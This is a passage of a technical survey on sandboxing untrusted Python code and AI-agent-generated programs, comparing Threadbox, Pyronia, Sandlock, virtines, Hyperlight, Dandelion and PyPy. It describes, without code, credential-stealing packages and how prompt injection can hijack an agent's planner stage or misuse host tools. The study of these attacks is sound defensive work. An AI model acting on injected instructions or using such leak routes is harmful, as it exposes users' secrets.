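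Python 3.15 also adds a function that lets C code make its own objects immortal. A developer working on NumPy, Python's main library for numerical arrays, requested it and reported in the forum thread *Add an Unstable C API for immortalizing objects* that making two shared objects immortal sped up a multithreaded test by about 20%. A host could use the function to build a table of exchange rates from immortal objects, put it on pages of its own and let the guest read it. The host would have to make every object in the table immortal and deal with any data that the objects store later. The change is permanent, and Python never frees the memory. That's fine for a table that the host loads once, but a server that did this for every customer's upload would eventually run out of memory.

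Python 3.15 also has a read-only dictionary type, `frozendict`. According to Python's release notes, one of its contributors was Victor Stinner, who had wanted a type like this for pysandbox. `frozendict` stops Python code from changing the dictionary's contents, but it doesn't make the dictionary's memory read-only.

The other major change is free threading, a version of CPython in which several threads can execute Python code at once. It replaces the single count with two, one for the thread that created the object and one for all other threads. Both are still in the object's header, so reading an ordinary object still writes to it. Deferred reference counting lets the interpreter skip some updates, but C code still makes them. Free threading does store counts outside the object, in a separate array for each thread, but only for a few types that many threads share. A more recent Python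 Enhancement Proposal would shrink the header but keep both counts and the collector's data in it.

Python 3.15 may help indirectly with its new stable binary interface for extensions that support free threading. Extensions that use it can no longer build the object header into their own data structures, which should make the header easier to redesign. For now, a host can prepare special read-only data for a guest, but it can't share an ordinary Python object read-only without the problem that Ghosn and colleagues found.

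### A guest with a secret and a network connection

In both Go and Python, an enclosure can't share part of a package. In the original receipt program, the upload and the signing key both belong to the main program, so giving `parse` read access to the upload would also give it the key. The example above therefore moves the uploads into their own package, and Ghosn and colleagues recommend splitting packages in the same way. Their image test instead gave Bild read access to the entire main package, which was reasonable only because the enclosure blocked all system calls.

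Many useful packages need system calls, and some also need a secret. For example, the Python package `ssh-decorater` logs in to another computer over SSH, a protocol for secure remote access, and runs Python commands there. It needs the user's login credentials and a network connection. Somebody added code to it that sent the credentials to a different server. A memory view can't stop this, because the package has to read the credentials to log in.

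Ghosn and colleagues recreated the attack and found two ways to block it. In the first, the trusted program opens the connection itself and passes it to the enclosed package along with the private key. The package then doesn't need to open connections or files, so the policy can forbid both. In the second, the package may open connections, but only to addresses on a list.

Neither fix is complete, because the package can still send the key to the computer it is supposed to log in to, and an attacker who controls that computer can pass it on. Ghosn and colleagues acknowledge this and warn that any system call could be used to leak data. A safer interface would keep the key in the host and let the package request only the signature that a login requires, although a malicious package could still request signatures for logins the user did not want.

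Still, both fixes leave far fewer places to send a stolen key. They work by restricting system calls, which the kernel can do without a modified compiler or interpreter.

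## Kernel permissions for a thread or a process: Threadbox and Sandlock

The Linux kernel carries out every system call, so it can block a request to open a file or a network connection whether the request comes from Python code or from a native extension. But it can't identify which Python function made the request, because it tracks processes and their threads, and functions exist only inside the interpreter. If `handle` may write to the disk and `parse` may not, a write from either function still reaches the kernel as the same kind of request from the same process.

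Threadbox, a research system from 2025, gets around this by running a function in its own thread. An older system called Pyronia has the interpreter report which functions are running. Sandlock confines a whole process, so untrusted Python code needs its own interpreter.

### What Linux can already restrict

All three systems build on existing parts of Linux. One of these parts is *seccomp*, which lets a program install a filter that decides which system calls it may make from then on. Chrome, Firefox and the common container systems all use it. However, a program passes a file name to the kernel as a pointer, and a seccomp filter can't follow pointers. Brandt, Morris and colleagues (2025) point out in *Locking Down Science Gateways with Landlock and Seccomp* that a filter can forbid opening files altogether, but can't distinguish the password file from a scratch file. The Linux kernel documentation's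 *Seccomp BPF (SECure COMPuting with filters)* page states that "System call filtering isn't a sandbox" and describes it as a tool for people who build sandboxes.

Another part is the Linux Security Modules framework, which places hooks in the kernel's code where a security module can refuse an action. Administrators use modules such as AppArmor and SELinux to restrict whole programs. A newer module, Landlock, lets any program restrict itself without an administrator's help. According to *Landlock* (Salaün, 2026), a program can limit itself to particular directories and network ports. It can tighten these rules later but never loosen them, and every thread and process it starts inherits them.

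New threads and processes inherit seccomp filters too. This makes the filters harder to escape, but it's awkward for a program whose parts need different permissions. For example, Flask, a popular Python web framework, typically starts a new thread for each request. Those threads can't gain any permission that the main thread lacks, so the main thread must have every permission that any of them needs.

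### Threadbox: one thread per function

Alhindi and Hallett (2025), in *Threadbox*, wrote a new security module that attaches permissions to single threads and doesn't pass them on. A programmer restricts a Python function by putting a *decorator* above it, a line that tells Python to wrap the function in extra code. The receipt program could do this:

```python
@sandbox_function("")             # no special permissions
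def safe_parse(upload):
    return parse(upload)
```

When `handle` calls `safe_parse`, the decorator starts a new thread, and the calling thread waits for the result. The new thread writes its list of permissions to a special file that the kernel module provides, and the module stores the list with the thread's number. The new thread then runs `parse`, and the module checks the list whenever `parse` tries to do something that needs a permission. A thread can submit a list only once, so `parse` can't give itself more permissions.

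There are seven permissions:

| Permission | What it allows |
|---|---|
| `rpath` | Read files |
| `wpath` | Create, change and delete files |
| `net` | Use the network |
| `proc` | Start new processes |
| `threading` | Start new threads |
| `gui` or `ipc` | Communicate with local programs, including the one that draws windows |
| `id` | Change user identities |

Alhindi and Hallett adapted Threadbox's permissions from Pledge, a similar mechanism in the operating system OpenBSD that has 33 permissions. They wanted programmers who know little about system calls to be able to use Threadbox's permissions. In one test, they restricted the part of a Java program that reads PDF files. This took two permissions in Threadbox, whereas seccomp would have required them to allow 25 system calls, which they could identify only by tracing the program and filtering the output.

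Programmers can find out which permissions a function needs by running it in learning mode, where the module allows everything and logs each permission the function uses. For a website's login page, the log listed `rpath` and `net`. The log only covers what happened during the trial, so if a function reads a file only when something goes wrong, a programmer may miss that permission.

Alhindi and Hallett used the decorator on five functions of magic-wormhole, a Python program for sending files between computers. Over 50 runs, the median time to receive data rose by 1.7% for a text, 3.5% for a file and 2.4% for a folder. These figures are a poor measure of the overhead of one call, because each transfer took well over a second and used only one or two of the restricted functions. Each call to a restricted function starts a new thread, so the overhead grows with the number of calls.

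Alhindi and Hallett also tested a Flask website. Flask already started a thread for each request, so the site didn't need the decorator. One line added at the top of each function set the permissions. Over 1,000 requests to one page, the median response time rose by 9%, from 21.8 to 23.8 milliseconds, and throughput fell from 460 to 404 requests per second. They list this as a 14% drop, but it is 12% of the original 460.

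Programs that don't use Threadbox also become slightly slower, because the kernel calls the module's hooks for every program on the machine. Accepting a network connection took 15% longer and opening a file took 3% to 9% longer, but each increase was less than 0.3 microseconds.

### What a restricted thread can still do

To test the website's security, Alhindi and Hallett let users upload files in YAML, a text format for structured data, which the website read with a function known to be unsafe. They uploaded a file containing an instruction to run a shell command and print the list of user accounts. The kernel blocked the command because starting one requires `proc`, which the page didn't have.

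However, the page did have `rpath` and `net`, so a slightly different attack could have read the same list from within Python and sent it over the network. Threadbox would have allowed both steps because its permissions don't specify which files or which servers. Likewise, the function that unpacks received folders in magic-wormhole has `wpath`, so an attacker who took it over could change any file that the user can change, including scripts that run the next time the user logs in.

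A bigger problem for the receipt program is that threads share memory, so `parse` can still read the signing key. It can't send the key anywhere itself, but it could hide the key in the list of orders it returns. It could also replace `sign` with its own function, which the host's unrestricted thread would then run. Restricting the main thread as well would limit the damage, but that thread needs most of the program's permissions.

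Threads also share open files and network connections. Alhindi and Hallett acknowledge all this sharing but argue that limiting what a thread can do with the data still helps. Landlock's developers, however, treated one restriction between threads as a bug and removed it because, as Salaün writes, "threads are not security boundaries". It had prevented a restricted thread from sending signals to differently restricted threads in the same process.

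New threads and processes don't inherit restrictions, so a guest with `proc` can start an unrestricted process. Alhindi and Hallett consider `threading` safer because a new thread can only run functions inside the program. But the new thread is also unrestricted, so one of those functions could start a process. Either permission effectively gives a hostile guest all the others.

Finally, if a guest tries something forbidden, the kernel kills the whole process, including the host, as with Enclosures.

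Threadbox is therefore a convenient safety net for code that is buggy but not hostile. Using it takes one line per function, and it stops common attacks that start a shell or contact a server from code that has no reason to do either. It doesn't protect secrets held in the same process.

### Pyronia: checking the call stack

*Pyronia* (Melara, Liu and Freedman, 2019) takes a different approach for smart cameras, speakers and similar devices, which often run a single Python program with many libraries. A library that recognizes faces, for example, should be able to read the photo but not the file with the owner's password.

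To use Pyronia, the developer leaves the program unchanged and writes one policy file that lists library functions and the files or network addresses each may use. When any code in the program tries to open a file, Pyronia's kernel module, an extension of AppArmor, pauses the request and contacts a helper thread inside the Python process. The helper pauses the interpreter and sends back the call stack, the list of functions currently running, each called by the one before. The kernel grants the request only if every function on the stack that appears in the policy has permission for that file.

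This prevents confused deputies. If a listed function without access to the password file calls another function that has access, the kernel refuses access because both are on the stack. The kernel generally skips functions that the policy doesn't mention, which saves developers a lot of work. They couldn't write rules for every library. Among 85 programs for such devices, Melara and colleagues found that the median program had libraries nested 25 levels deep.

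The call stack is in ordinary memory, though, and 41 of the 50 most popular libraries in Melara and colleagues' sample included C or C++ code, which could forge it. Pyronia therefore keeps the stack on protected pages and makes them writable only while the interpreter needs to change them. The interpreter needs to do this almost all the time, because Python updates reference counts, including those in the stack's own frames, for practically every instruction. The researchers counted millions of permission changes in a single round of each test program, and these caused most of the slowdown. Reference counts also slowed down the Python version of Enclosures.

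The team tested three programs: one that posts photos to Twitter, a smart speaker and a plant monitor. A single run, including startup, took two to five times as long as in ordinary Python. Over 100 rounds, the slowdown was two to three times, and memory use rose by 39% on average. The programs did little work, so even the slowest round took only 1.5 seconds. Nobody would notice that delay in a camera that posts a photo every 15 minutes, but Melara and colleagues thought users of the smart speaker probably would.

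Pyronia blocked a malicious library function that tried to upload a private login key in place of a photo, another that tried to send the photo to an unapproved server, and a third that tried to run a shell command. The rules that blocked them are more specific than Threadbox can express. But Melara and colleagues had to trust the hardware, the operating system and the whole Python interpreter. They also protected only the stack, so `parse` could still read the signing key from memory. Python stored each function's local variables outside the protected pages, so a hostile library could change the arguments of a function that had more permissions. The prototype runs Python 2.7 and supports only single-threaded programs.

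In her dissertation, *Intra-Process Least Privilege and Isolation for Emerging Applications*, Melara (2019) argues that developers rarely put each library in its own process because they would have to restructure their programs, and because processes take much longer to exchange data than functions do. These are good reasons when a program passes live objects back and forth with dozens of libraries, but they're weaker when the guest is a separate script that takes a file and returns a list, or a command that an AI agent has just written.

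### Sandlock: fixed rules and a supervisor

Wang and Zheng designed Sandlock for the many short commands that agents run on a programmer's own computer, next to private keys and source code. It needs no administrator rights and no container image, the bundle of files that a system like Docker has to prepare first.

To run a command, Sandlock creates a child process, which applies Landlock rules and a seccomp filter to itself. The child waits until the parent is ready to supervise it, closes its inherited files except standard input and output, and then starts the command. It must close the files first because Landlock doesn't restrict files that were already open.

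Wang and Zheng divide the policy into two parts. The kernel alone enforces rules that Sandlock can set before the guest starts, such as which directories it may read. Everything else goes to the *supervisor*, a part of Sandlock that runs outside the guest. The kernel pauses certain system calls and lets the supervisor decide about them. This allows rules that Landlock can't express, such as letting the guest send requests to one URL on a website but not to the rest of the site. For encrypted traffic, such a rule works only if the guest accepts a special certificate that lets Sandlock read the requests.

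The supervisor can also change the policy while the guest is running. Installing a package requires network access, but the tests that follow usually don't. The programmer can supply a function that cuts off network access when the tests begin. Wang and Zheng warn against using such a function to block commands by name, because hostile code can rename a program.

Supervisors of this kind have a known weakness. According to the Linux manual page *seccomp_unotify(2)*, the mechanism they use is explicitly not intended for implementing security policy. A supervisor might read a connection's destination from the guest's memory, approve it and let the kernel continue, but the kernel then reads the destination again, and another thread of the guest may have changed it in the meantime. Sandlock avoids this by copying the address, checking the copy and making the connection itself on the guest's behalf.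 It refuses any request it can't decide on safely.

Sandlock adds 5 milliseconds to a program's startup time, far less than a container does. In a test reported in the project's documentation, Docs.rs' *sandlock-cli 0.8.3*, `echo` took 2 milliseconds by itself, 7 in Sandlock and 307 in Docker. Rules that the kernel enforces without the supervisor added no measurable overhead to the Redis database. When the supervisor had to handle each network message, a short exchange between two local programs took 55 microseconds instead of 20. That delay would matter for a busy local database, but not for an agent that waits a second or more for a language model to answer.

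### Stages with different permissions

Sandlock can also connect several confined processes in a pipeline, where each one sends its output to the next through a *pipe*, a one-way channel that the kernel provides. Each stage has its own policy. The receipt program could use two stages:

```python
reader = Sandbox(fs_readable=["/usr", "/lib", "/uploads"])
parser = Sandbox(fs_readable=["/usr", "/lib", "/guest"],
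                 clean_env=True)
result = (
    reader.cmd(["cat", path])
    | parser.cmd(["python3", "/guest/parse.py"])
).run()
orders = json.loads(result.stdout)
```

The reader may open the uploaded files, and the parser receives only the bytes of one of them. Neither can use the network, which Sandlock blocks by default. The setting `clean_env` removes the host's environment variables, in case one of them contains the key. The parser runs in a new Python interpreter that has never loaded the key, and Landlock prevents it from using the system's debugging functions to read the host's memory.

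The two sizes of boundary compare as follows:

| | Thread in Threadbox | Process in Sandlock |
|---|---|---|
| Host's memory | Guest can read and change it | Separate |
| Host's open files | Shared | Closed before the guest starts |
| Threads and processes that the guest starts | Unrestricted | Inherit the guest's restrictions |
| Forbidden request | Kernel kills guest and host together | Guest usually gets an error, and the host continues |
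| Passing data | By reference | As bytes through a pipe |

Wang and Zheng built pipelines mainly to limit prompt injection, in which instructions hidden in a web page or file take control of an AI agent. The worst cases occur when one agent has private data, reads untrusted content and can communicate with the outside. A single process often needs all three for legitimate reasons, so confining it doesn't help much. A pipeline lets the programmer deny the network to the stage that reads untrusted content and deny private data to the stage that has the network.

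A hijacked stage can still influence the next one through what it writes to the pipe. In an example from the Sandlock documentation, a planner writes shell commands and an executor runs them. The executor can read private files but can't use the network. If an attacker hijacks the planner, the executor will run the attacker's commands and can print the files, so whatever receives its output must treat that output as private. In the receipt program, a hostile parser can't steal the key, but it can invent orders for the host to sign. Wang and Zheng acknowledge this problem and leave it to the programmer to divide the task sensibly.

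### The overhead of passing data

The host and the parser can no longer share objects, so they have to serialize the list of orders. The example uses JSON, which avoids the danger of loading a pickle from the guest.

Wang and Zheng don't report how long data takes to pass through a pipe, but their network test gives a rough idea. Without Sandlock, two local programs exchanged a 256-byte message and a reply in 20 microseconds. The supervisor doesn't handle ordinary reads and writes on a pipe, so a similar exchange between stages should take roughly as long. If the host sent a 10,000-line file one line at a time and waited for each answer, the exchanges would add about 0.2 seconds, roughly 500 times as much as an Enclosure in Go with protection keys would add. Sending the entire file at once, as the pipeline does, is far better because the main overhead is then starting the sandbox and a new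 Python interpreter once per upload.

If a guest needs a table of several gigabytes for every call, copying it each time could take longer than the work itself. Sandlock can instead load the data once and then *fork* the process, which creates a copy that shares the original's memory until one of them changes it. In Wang and Zheng's test, creating 1,000 confined copies took 0.53 seconds, about half a millisecond each. Forking would also be a fast way to give every upload a fresh interpreter. But each copy starts with everything in the original's memory, so the host would have to fork from a process that had never loaded the key.

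### The shared kernel

Wang and Zheng tested Sandlock on ten simple cases, such as reading a forbidden file, and it handled all of them correctly. The tests show that the rules work as intended, but they weren't attempts to break out. Brandt and colleagues did try to break out of Landlock, which they combined with seccomp to protect astrophysics programs that outsiders can use through a website. They tried to gain administrator rights with several tricks involving `sudo`, and they opened a new shell from inside a text editor. Landlock's restrictions held each time, but they found that a guest can discover whether a file exists in a forbidden directory by guessing its name. At the time Landlock also couldn't restrict UDP, a network protocol that attackers can use to smuggle out data, so Brandt and colleagues blocked it with seccomp. Landlock has since added rules for UDP ports.

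Wang and Zheng expect many failures to come from mistakes in the policy, such as allowing a program that can itself run arbitrary commands. A guest may also try to use up the machine's memory or keep starting new processes. Sandlock limits both, but Wang and Zheng say its limits are better suited to buggy programs than to determined attackers.

The most serious risk is a bug in the kernel, which enforces the rules and also serves the guest's requests. In 2026, researchers published Linux vulnerabilities called Copy Fail and Dirty Frag, which let a program alter the kernel's copy of any file it can read. Brandt and colleagues note that Landlock can't prevent such an attack, although its other restrictions may make one harder to carry out. For services where customers may attack one another, Wang and Zheng recommend small virtual machines with their own kernels.

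## A virtual machine for one function call: virtines and Hyperlight

A guest with its own kernel can't attack the host's kernel through ordinary system calls, but a standard Linux virtual machine takes hundreds of milliseconds to start. A function like `parse` doesn't need most of what starts in that time, such as a file system and device drivers. *Isolating Functions at the Hardware Limit with Virtines* (Wanninger, Bowden and colleagues, 2022) introduced the *virtine*, a virtual machine that runs one call to one function without an operating system and can start in microseconds.

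The method suits C, where a function can run without most of the program around it. To run a JavaScript function this way, the team had to put a whole JavaScript engine into the virtual machine.

### Cutting a function out of a C program

The programmer marks a function with the keyword `virtine`. In a C version of the receipt program, this could look as follows:

```c
virtine struct orders parse(struct upload file) {
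    /* the outside parser */
}
```

A modified compiler finds every function that `parse` calls, directly or through others, and packs them into a separate image with startup code and a small C library. A typical image is about 16 KB. When the host program calls `parse`, it copies the arguments into a new virtual machine, runs the image and waits for the result. The call is written like any other function call.

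The guest can't access the host's memory, so `struct upload` has to contain the bytes of the file rather than a pointer to the host's heap. The compiler gives the guest a copy of each global variable that its code uses, so a malicious parser could get the signing key by mentioning `SIGNING_KEY` in its source code. The host's programmer should keep untrusted code in a separate source file where the key isn't visible.

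Wanninger and colleagues wrote Wasp, a hypervisor (software that creates and controls virtual machines). It is a library that runs inside the host program and uses the virtualization features of Linux or Windows. The guest has no virtual disk or network card, and can reach the outside only through a *hypercall*, a request that pauses the virtual machine and returns control to Wasp. By default, Wasp allows only the hypercall that ends the guest's run.

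The host's programmer can allow more hypercalls, and a handler function in the host checks and carries out each request. One hypercall can do a complete task, such as reading from a file, that would take many exchanges with a virtual disk. The guest's C library turns its system calls into hypercalls, so ordinary C code can still read a file if the policy allows it.

The handlers belong to the trusted computing base, along with Wasp, the host's kernel and the processor. A handler that opens any file the guest names would be a confused deputy. Wanninger and colleagues expect specialists to write the handlers. They also assume that the guest can't extract secrets through hardware side effects such as timing, but acknowledge that flaws like Meltdown could make this possible.

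### Pools and snapshots

Even when a virtual machine has no operating system, the host's kernel has to create it, and startup code has to switch the virtual processor from its initial 16-bit mode to 64-bit mode and set up page tables. The startup code takes about 12 microseconds, mostly for the page tables.

Wasp saves time on the first task by keeping a pool of used virtual machines. When a call ends, Wasp clears the machine's memory and keeps the empty shell for a later call. If it clears the memory in the background, preparing a shell takes only 4% longer than just entering and leaving a virtual machine. Preparing a shell this way is much faster than creating a Linux thread, which Threadbox does for each call.

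Snapshots save time on the second task. The first call to a function goes through the whole startup, and Wasp then saves a copy of the virtual machine's memory. Later calls start from this copy. For a function that did almost no work, snapshots made calls 2.5 times faster.

As with Sandlock's forked processes, every later call starts with whatever was in memory when the host took the snapshot, so the host must take it before the guest receives any private data.

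### How much work makes a call worthwhile

Entering and leaving a virtine takes about 5 microseconds, compared with 0.9 for an Enclosure that uses VT-x. In return, the virtine's guest gets fresh memory for each call.

To find out when this overhead stops mattering, Wanninger and colleagues ran a function that calculates Fibonacci numbers. The smallest calls took 6.6 times as long in a virtine as without a sandbox. Calculating the 25th number took 3% longer, and the 30th took 1% longer. They concluded that about 100 microseconds of work is enough to make the startup overhead negligible.

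Requests to the host, called hypercalls, add to the overhead. In a simple web server, the team handled each connection in its own virtine, which made seven hypercalls to read the request, find and read a file, send the response and exit. Each hypercall left the virtual machine, passed through the host's kernel to Wasp, and usually returned to the kernel to carry out the operation. The server handled only 12% fewer requests per second than it did without virtines. A server that did more work between hypercalls would probably lose less throughput.

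The worst result came from the encryption library OpenSSL. An experienced developer needed about an hour to move its AES cipher into a virtine, and most of the effort went into changing how OpenSSL was compiled. The cipher then ran 17 times slower on 16 KB blocks of data. The test program called it thousands of times per second, and each call copied a 21 KB image into a virtual machine. Wanninger and colleagues had chosen the cipher to see how hard the change would be, and they recommend putting a larger piece of work in each virtine in practice.

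They estimate that an image of this size takes 16 microseconds to start. If a C parser of the same size ran in a fresh virtual machine for each line of a 10,000-line file, starting the virtual machines would take 0.16 seconds in total, compared with 50 seconds for Sandlock's processes.

Larger images take longer to start because Wasp copies the whole snapshot for each call. An image padded with zeros to 16 MB took 2.3 milliseconds, about as long as the computer needed to copy 16 MB of memory. The team expected a large improvement from *copy-on-write*, the kind of memory sharing that Sandlock's forked processes use.

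### One JavaScript function and its engine

The compiler can extract a C function from a program because the function and everything it calls become machine code. A JavaScript function needs an engine to run it, just as Python code needs an interpreter. Wanninger and colleagues therefore compiled the entire Duktape engine into the virtine's image, which came to about 578 KB.

The test function converted a buffer of data to base64, a way of writing binary data as text. The guest could make three hypercalls: one to take a snapshot after the engine had started, one to fetch the data and one to return the result and exit. It could make each of the first two only once, so an attacker who took over the engine after both had been used could do nothing except return a false result.

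A call took 419 microseconds without a sandbox and 125 microseconds longer in a virtine without a snapshot. With a snapshot and one further change, the call took 137 microseconds in a virtine, about a third of the time without a sandbox.

The virtine saved time by avoiding setup and cleanup, but the JavaScript itself ran no faster. For each call, the native program created a new engine, connected it to several host functions, ran the script and then freed the engine's memory piece by piece. The virtine could skip the setup because its snapshot already contained a working engine. A further change skipped the cleanup too, since Wasp clears the whole virtual machine anyway. According to Wanninger and colleagues, the remaining 137 microseconds were essentially the time to parse and run the script. Copying the snapshot may account for more of that time than they suggest, because copying its 578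 KB would take about 83 microseconds at the speed they measured for the 16 MB image.

A native program could also avoid most of the setup by reusing the same engine for every call. But a script could then leave data behind, or replace a function that the next customer's script uses. With a snapshot, each call gets an engine that is already set up and that no earlier script has changed.

For an interpreted language, a sandbox for one call has to contain an interpreter. This removes the main difficulty that Enclosures had with Python, because the guest can update the reference counts of its own objects. But the host has to copy all data into and out of the sandbox, and for each call it has to start an interpreter or restore one from a snapshot.

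This would be harder for most languages than it looks with Duktape, a small engine without a just-in-time compiler, which modern engines use to turn frequently executed code into machine code. Wanninger and colleagues thought V8, Chrome's engine, could also run in a virtine, but only after somebody adapted the C++ standard library. If a Python interpreter and its libraries took up 16 MB, copying them would add 2.3 milliseconds to every call.

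The team also built Vespid, a prototype cloud service that runs each customer's function in a Duktape virtine. It responded faster to sudden bursts of requests than Apache OpenWhisk, which uses containers. However, the comparison favored Vespid because OpenWhisk used the larger V8 engine and lacked the snapshots and container reuse of newer research systems.

### Hyperlight: the same idea as a product

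Microsoft has since developed Hyperlight, an open-source library for this kind of sandbox. According to Microsoft's *Introducing Hyperlight* (2024), the guest gets a block of memory and a virtual processor, but no devices or operating system. The host chooses which of its own functions the guest may call. At the time, creating a virtual machine with Hyperlight took 1 to 2 milliseconds, compared with over 120 for an optimized ordinary one.

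In a conference demonstration, Hyperlight answered web requests in 0.9 milliseconds on average. Microsoft's *Hyperlight creating a 0.0009 second micro VM execution time* (2025) shows that this figure doesn't include creating a virtual machine, despite the title. The server took a machine from a pool, with its memory already set up and the guest program loaded. The guest called the host once to print a message, and Hyperlight then reset the machine's memory.

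This reset is optional. According to the Hyperlight project's README, the guest's state persists from one call to the next unless the host restores a snapshot. A host that needs a fresh domain for each customer's file must therefore restore a snapshot before every call. Restoring memory may not be enough, because a guest might store data in special processor registers. In *Disallow MSR read/writes*, ludfjig (2025) proposed blocking the guest's access to such registers so that no data could survive a restore.

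Guests also need special preparation because Hyperlight can't run ordinary programs or container images, according to its documentation. To run JavaScript, Microsoft's *Build a Hyperlight C guest to securely execute JavaScript* (2025) compiles the small engine QuickJS into the guest, much as Wanninger and colleagues did with Duktape. The developers had to remove the parts of QuickJS that use files or threads, which Hyperlight didn't support. The host can call only one function, which takes a script as a string and returns the result as a string.

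### Why the reported start times differ

By January 2026, Microsoft was describing Hyperlight's start time as low tens of milliseconds, not 1 to 2. The amount of memory may explain part of the difference. In a proposed change to the library, ludfjig (2026), in *Persist snapshot to disk*, measured the time from starting a sandbox to completing one trivial call. For each heap size, the developer compared a new sandbox with one that Hyperlight loaded from a snapshot on disk:

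| Guest's heap | New sandbox | Snapshot from disk |
|---|---|---|
| 128 KB | 3.80 ms | 2.78 ms |
| 8 MB | 8.89 ms | 2.96 ms |
| 64 MB | 26.7 ms | 2.92 ms |
| 256 MB | 88.3 ms | 3.33 ms |

The snapshot times don't include checking that the saved memory is intact, so they apply only where the host trusts the snapshot file. With the check, the largest snapshot took 57.4 milliseconds.

Large interpreters benefit most from this because they need a lot of memory. Hyperlight 0.14.0 also introduced copy-on-write for restoring snapshots, which Wanninger and colleagues had hoped for. According to the release notes, it reduces delay by up to 99%. Hyperlight's planned *Snapshot-First Sandbox Lifecycle* would start every sandbox from a stored snapshot, with a target of less than a millisecond.

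### Python inside Hyperlight

Hyperlight now has two main ways to run Python, and both put an interpreter in the virtual machine. One packages the interpreter as WebAssembly. Microsoft's *Hyperlight Wasm* points out that an attacker would then have to escape from WebAssembly before attacking the virtual machine.

The other way adds a small kernel inside the virtual machine. Microsoft's *Hyperlight Nanvix* (2026) describes one such kernel, Nanvix, which provides more than 150 system calls, enough to run CPython. When the guest tries to open a file, for example, the request passes through Nanvix to the host, which can allow, change or refuse it. Starting the kernel, the interpreter and the program takes tens of milliseconds.

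Nanvix makes existing software much easier to run, but it widens the interface to the host. The Duktape virtine could make three requests, while a host that supports ordinary Python programs has to handle many kinds of file and network operations safely. Microsoft lets the host move this work into a separate process or a second virtual machine to limit the damage from a mistake.

### Letting an agent write programs

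Microsoft also uses Hyperlight to run code that language models write. An AI agent normally calls one tool at a time, such as a function that looks up a customer's orders, and the model has to read each result before it requests the next call. In Microsoft's *CodeAct in Agent Framework* (2026), the model instead writes a short Python program that runs in Hyperlight, calls several tools and combines their results.

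In one test, an agent had to add up the orders of eight users, including discounts and taxes. Having the agent write a program for this reduced the time from 27.8 to 13.2 seconds and the number of tokens, the pieces of text that a model processes, from 6,890 to 2,489. The savings came from making fewer requests to the model, while Hyperlight made the generated program safer to run without adding much delay.

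The generated program can't access the host's files or the network unless the developer allows particular directories or websites. But the tools run in the host with all of its permissions. If the receipt program offered `sign` as a tool, a hostile guest could use it as a confused deputy to sign forged receipts. Similarly, a tool that downloads web pages can contact sites that the sandbox isn't allowed to contact.

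A person can approve the program before it runs, but the approval covers the whole program, not each tool call. Microsoft therefore recommends keeping actions such as sending email or spending money out of the sandbox, so the model has to request each one separately.

The documentation for Microsoft's *agent-framework-hyperlight* (2026), the package that implements this, warns of a similar gap in automatic checks. The framework's FIDES feature labels data and enforces rules about which tools may use it, but it doesn't check calls that come from inside a generated program, so the tools have to enforce such rules themselves.

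In April 2026, Microsoft said the first version created a new virtual machine for every program. By November, the package was reusing a virtual machine and restoring a snapshot of the ready interpreter before the next program. It also stopped guest code after 30 seconds by default, though it couldn't interrupt a tool running on the host. Error messages from tools can reveal private data, so the package replaces them with a generic message before they reach the guest.

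### Dandelion: separating calculation from communication

Many functions still need the network, and supporting it makes a sandbox slower to start. Kuchler, Li and colleagues (2025) measured this in *Unlocking True Elasticity for the Cloud-Native Era with Dandelion*, using Firecracker, Amazon's system for small virtual machines. Even from a snapshot, a trivial function took over 10 milliseconds to start, and more than 8 milliseconds of that was spent loading the guest's operating system and reconnecting it to the host.

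Cloud platforms usually avoid the startup delay by keeping idle sandboxes ready. Kuchler and colleagues used Knative, a common platform, to replay a record of real requests to Microsoft's cloud. A sandbox was ready for about 97% of requests, but the platform reserved 16 times as much memory as the active requests needed.

The Dandelion platform divides a program into two kinds of function. *Compute functions* contain the customer's untrusted code. They turn a declared set of inputs into a declared set of outputs and make no system calls. *Communication functions* belong to the platform, and customers can use but not change them. The prototype has one, which sends web requests.

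For example, a program that summarizes logs might start with a compute function that receives an access token and writes a web request. Dandelion sends the request and passes the reply, a list of log servers, to a second compute function, which writes a request for each server. Dandelion sends these requests too, so the customer's code never opens a network connection. A third compute function then combines the returned logs.

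Compute functions can still use ordinary file operations, because Dandelion presents their inputs and outputs as files in memory. A function that tries to open a connection or start a thread gets an error.

This small interface lets Dandelion run the same kind of function under four isolation mechanisms:

- a virtual machine, through Linux's KVM
- a Linux process
- CHERI, a hardware design with capabilities like those in the Morello processor
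- rWasm, which compiles WebAssembly

Dandelion's sandboxes start in hundreds of microseconds, or under 90 microseconds with CHERI. Dandelion can therefore start one for each request instead of keeping idle ones, and in the replay it reserved 96% less memory than Knative. Kuchler and colleagues don't recommend Dandelion for programs whose parts constantly share data, such as online games or AI training.

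Dividing a program this way doesn't by itself prevent leaks. In the log example, the first function holds the access token and also writes the request that Dandelion sends, so a malicious version could address the request to an attacker's server. The platform would also have to restrict where requests can go. The receipt program could avoid this problem, because `parse` needs no web requests and its output could go straight to the host for checking and signing.

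Dandelion's prototype also supports Python, again by supplying an interpreter. CPython normally relies on an operating system for files and much else, so to run it behind such a small interface, something else has to handle its system calls or make them unnecessary.

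## A whole Python interpreter behind a narrow interface: PyPy and WebAssembly

Python code mostly reaches the outside world through its interpreter, which turns a call such as `open("orders.txt")` into a request to the operating system. If the interpreter can send such requests only to the host, the host can let `parse` run arbitrary Python. The hidden paths between objects that defeated pysandbox still exist, but they lead only to other objects inside the sandbox.

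PyPy, an alternative to CPython, has had a sandbox of this kind for many years, but its developers stopped maintaining the sandbox and haven't released the replacement they began in 2019. Newer projects get a similar result by compiling CPython itself to WebAssembly.

### PyPy's controller

PyPy's developers wrote their interpreter in RPython, a restricted form of Python that a toolchain translates into C. According to PyPy's documentation, this toolchain can replace every call to an outside C function with code that writes the operation's name and arguments to a pipe and waits for an answer. The resulting interpreter runs in a subprocess, and a trusted program called the controller reads the pipe and decides how to handle each request.

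If `parse` tries to open a file, the controller receives the operation `os_open` and a path. It can refuse, open the real file or return a fake result. The demonstration controller presents a virtual directory tree that includes Python's standard library. It also invents the file descriptors it returns, so a guest can't reach the host's open files by trying other numbers. The policy is ordinary Python code, so it can be as specific as its author wants. A guest that only calculates never has to wait for the controller.

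PyPy's developers argue that the same sandboxing method would be unsafe with CPython, which is too easy to crash. PyPy's C code comes from a generator, so the developers only have to get the generator right. The sandboxed version also checks for errors such as buffer overflows while it runs.

This argument matters because the kernel doesn't restrict the subprocess. An attacker who managed to run machine code there could bypass the controller by making system calls directly. A host could guard against this with a strict seccomp filter, since the guest needs little more than the pipe and some memory.

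The sandbox never attracted many users. In 2015, when a developer considering it for a product asked about a missing operation, PyPy developer Armin Rigo replied that the sandbox was "mostly working" but lacked a champion (Rigo, 2015, *Sandbox missing functions like 'fcntl'*). It also couldn't load compiled Python modules, as a presentation published by CAE Community, a cybersecurity education network, points out.

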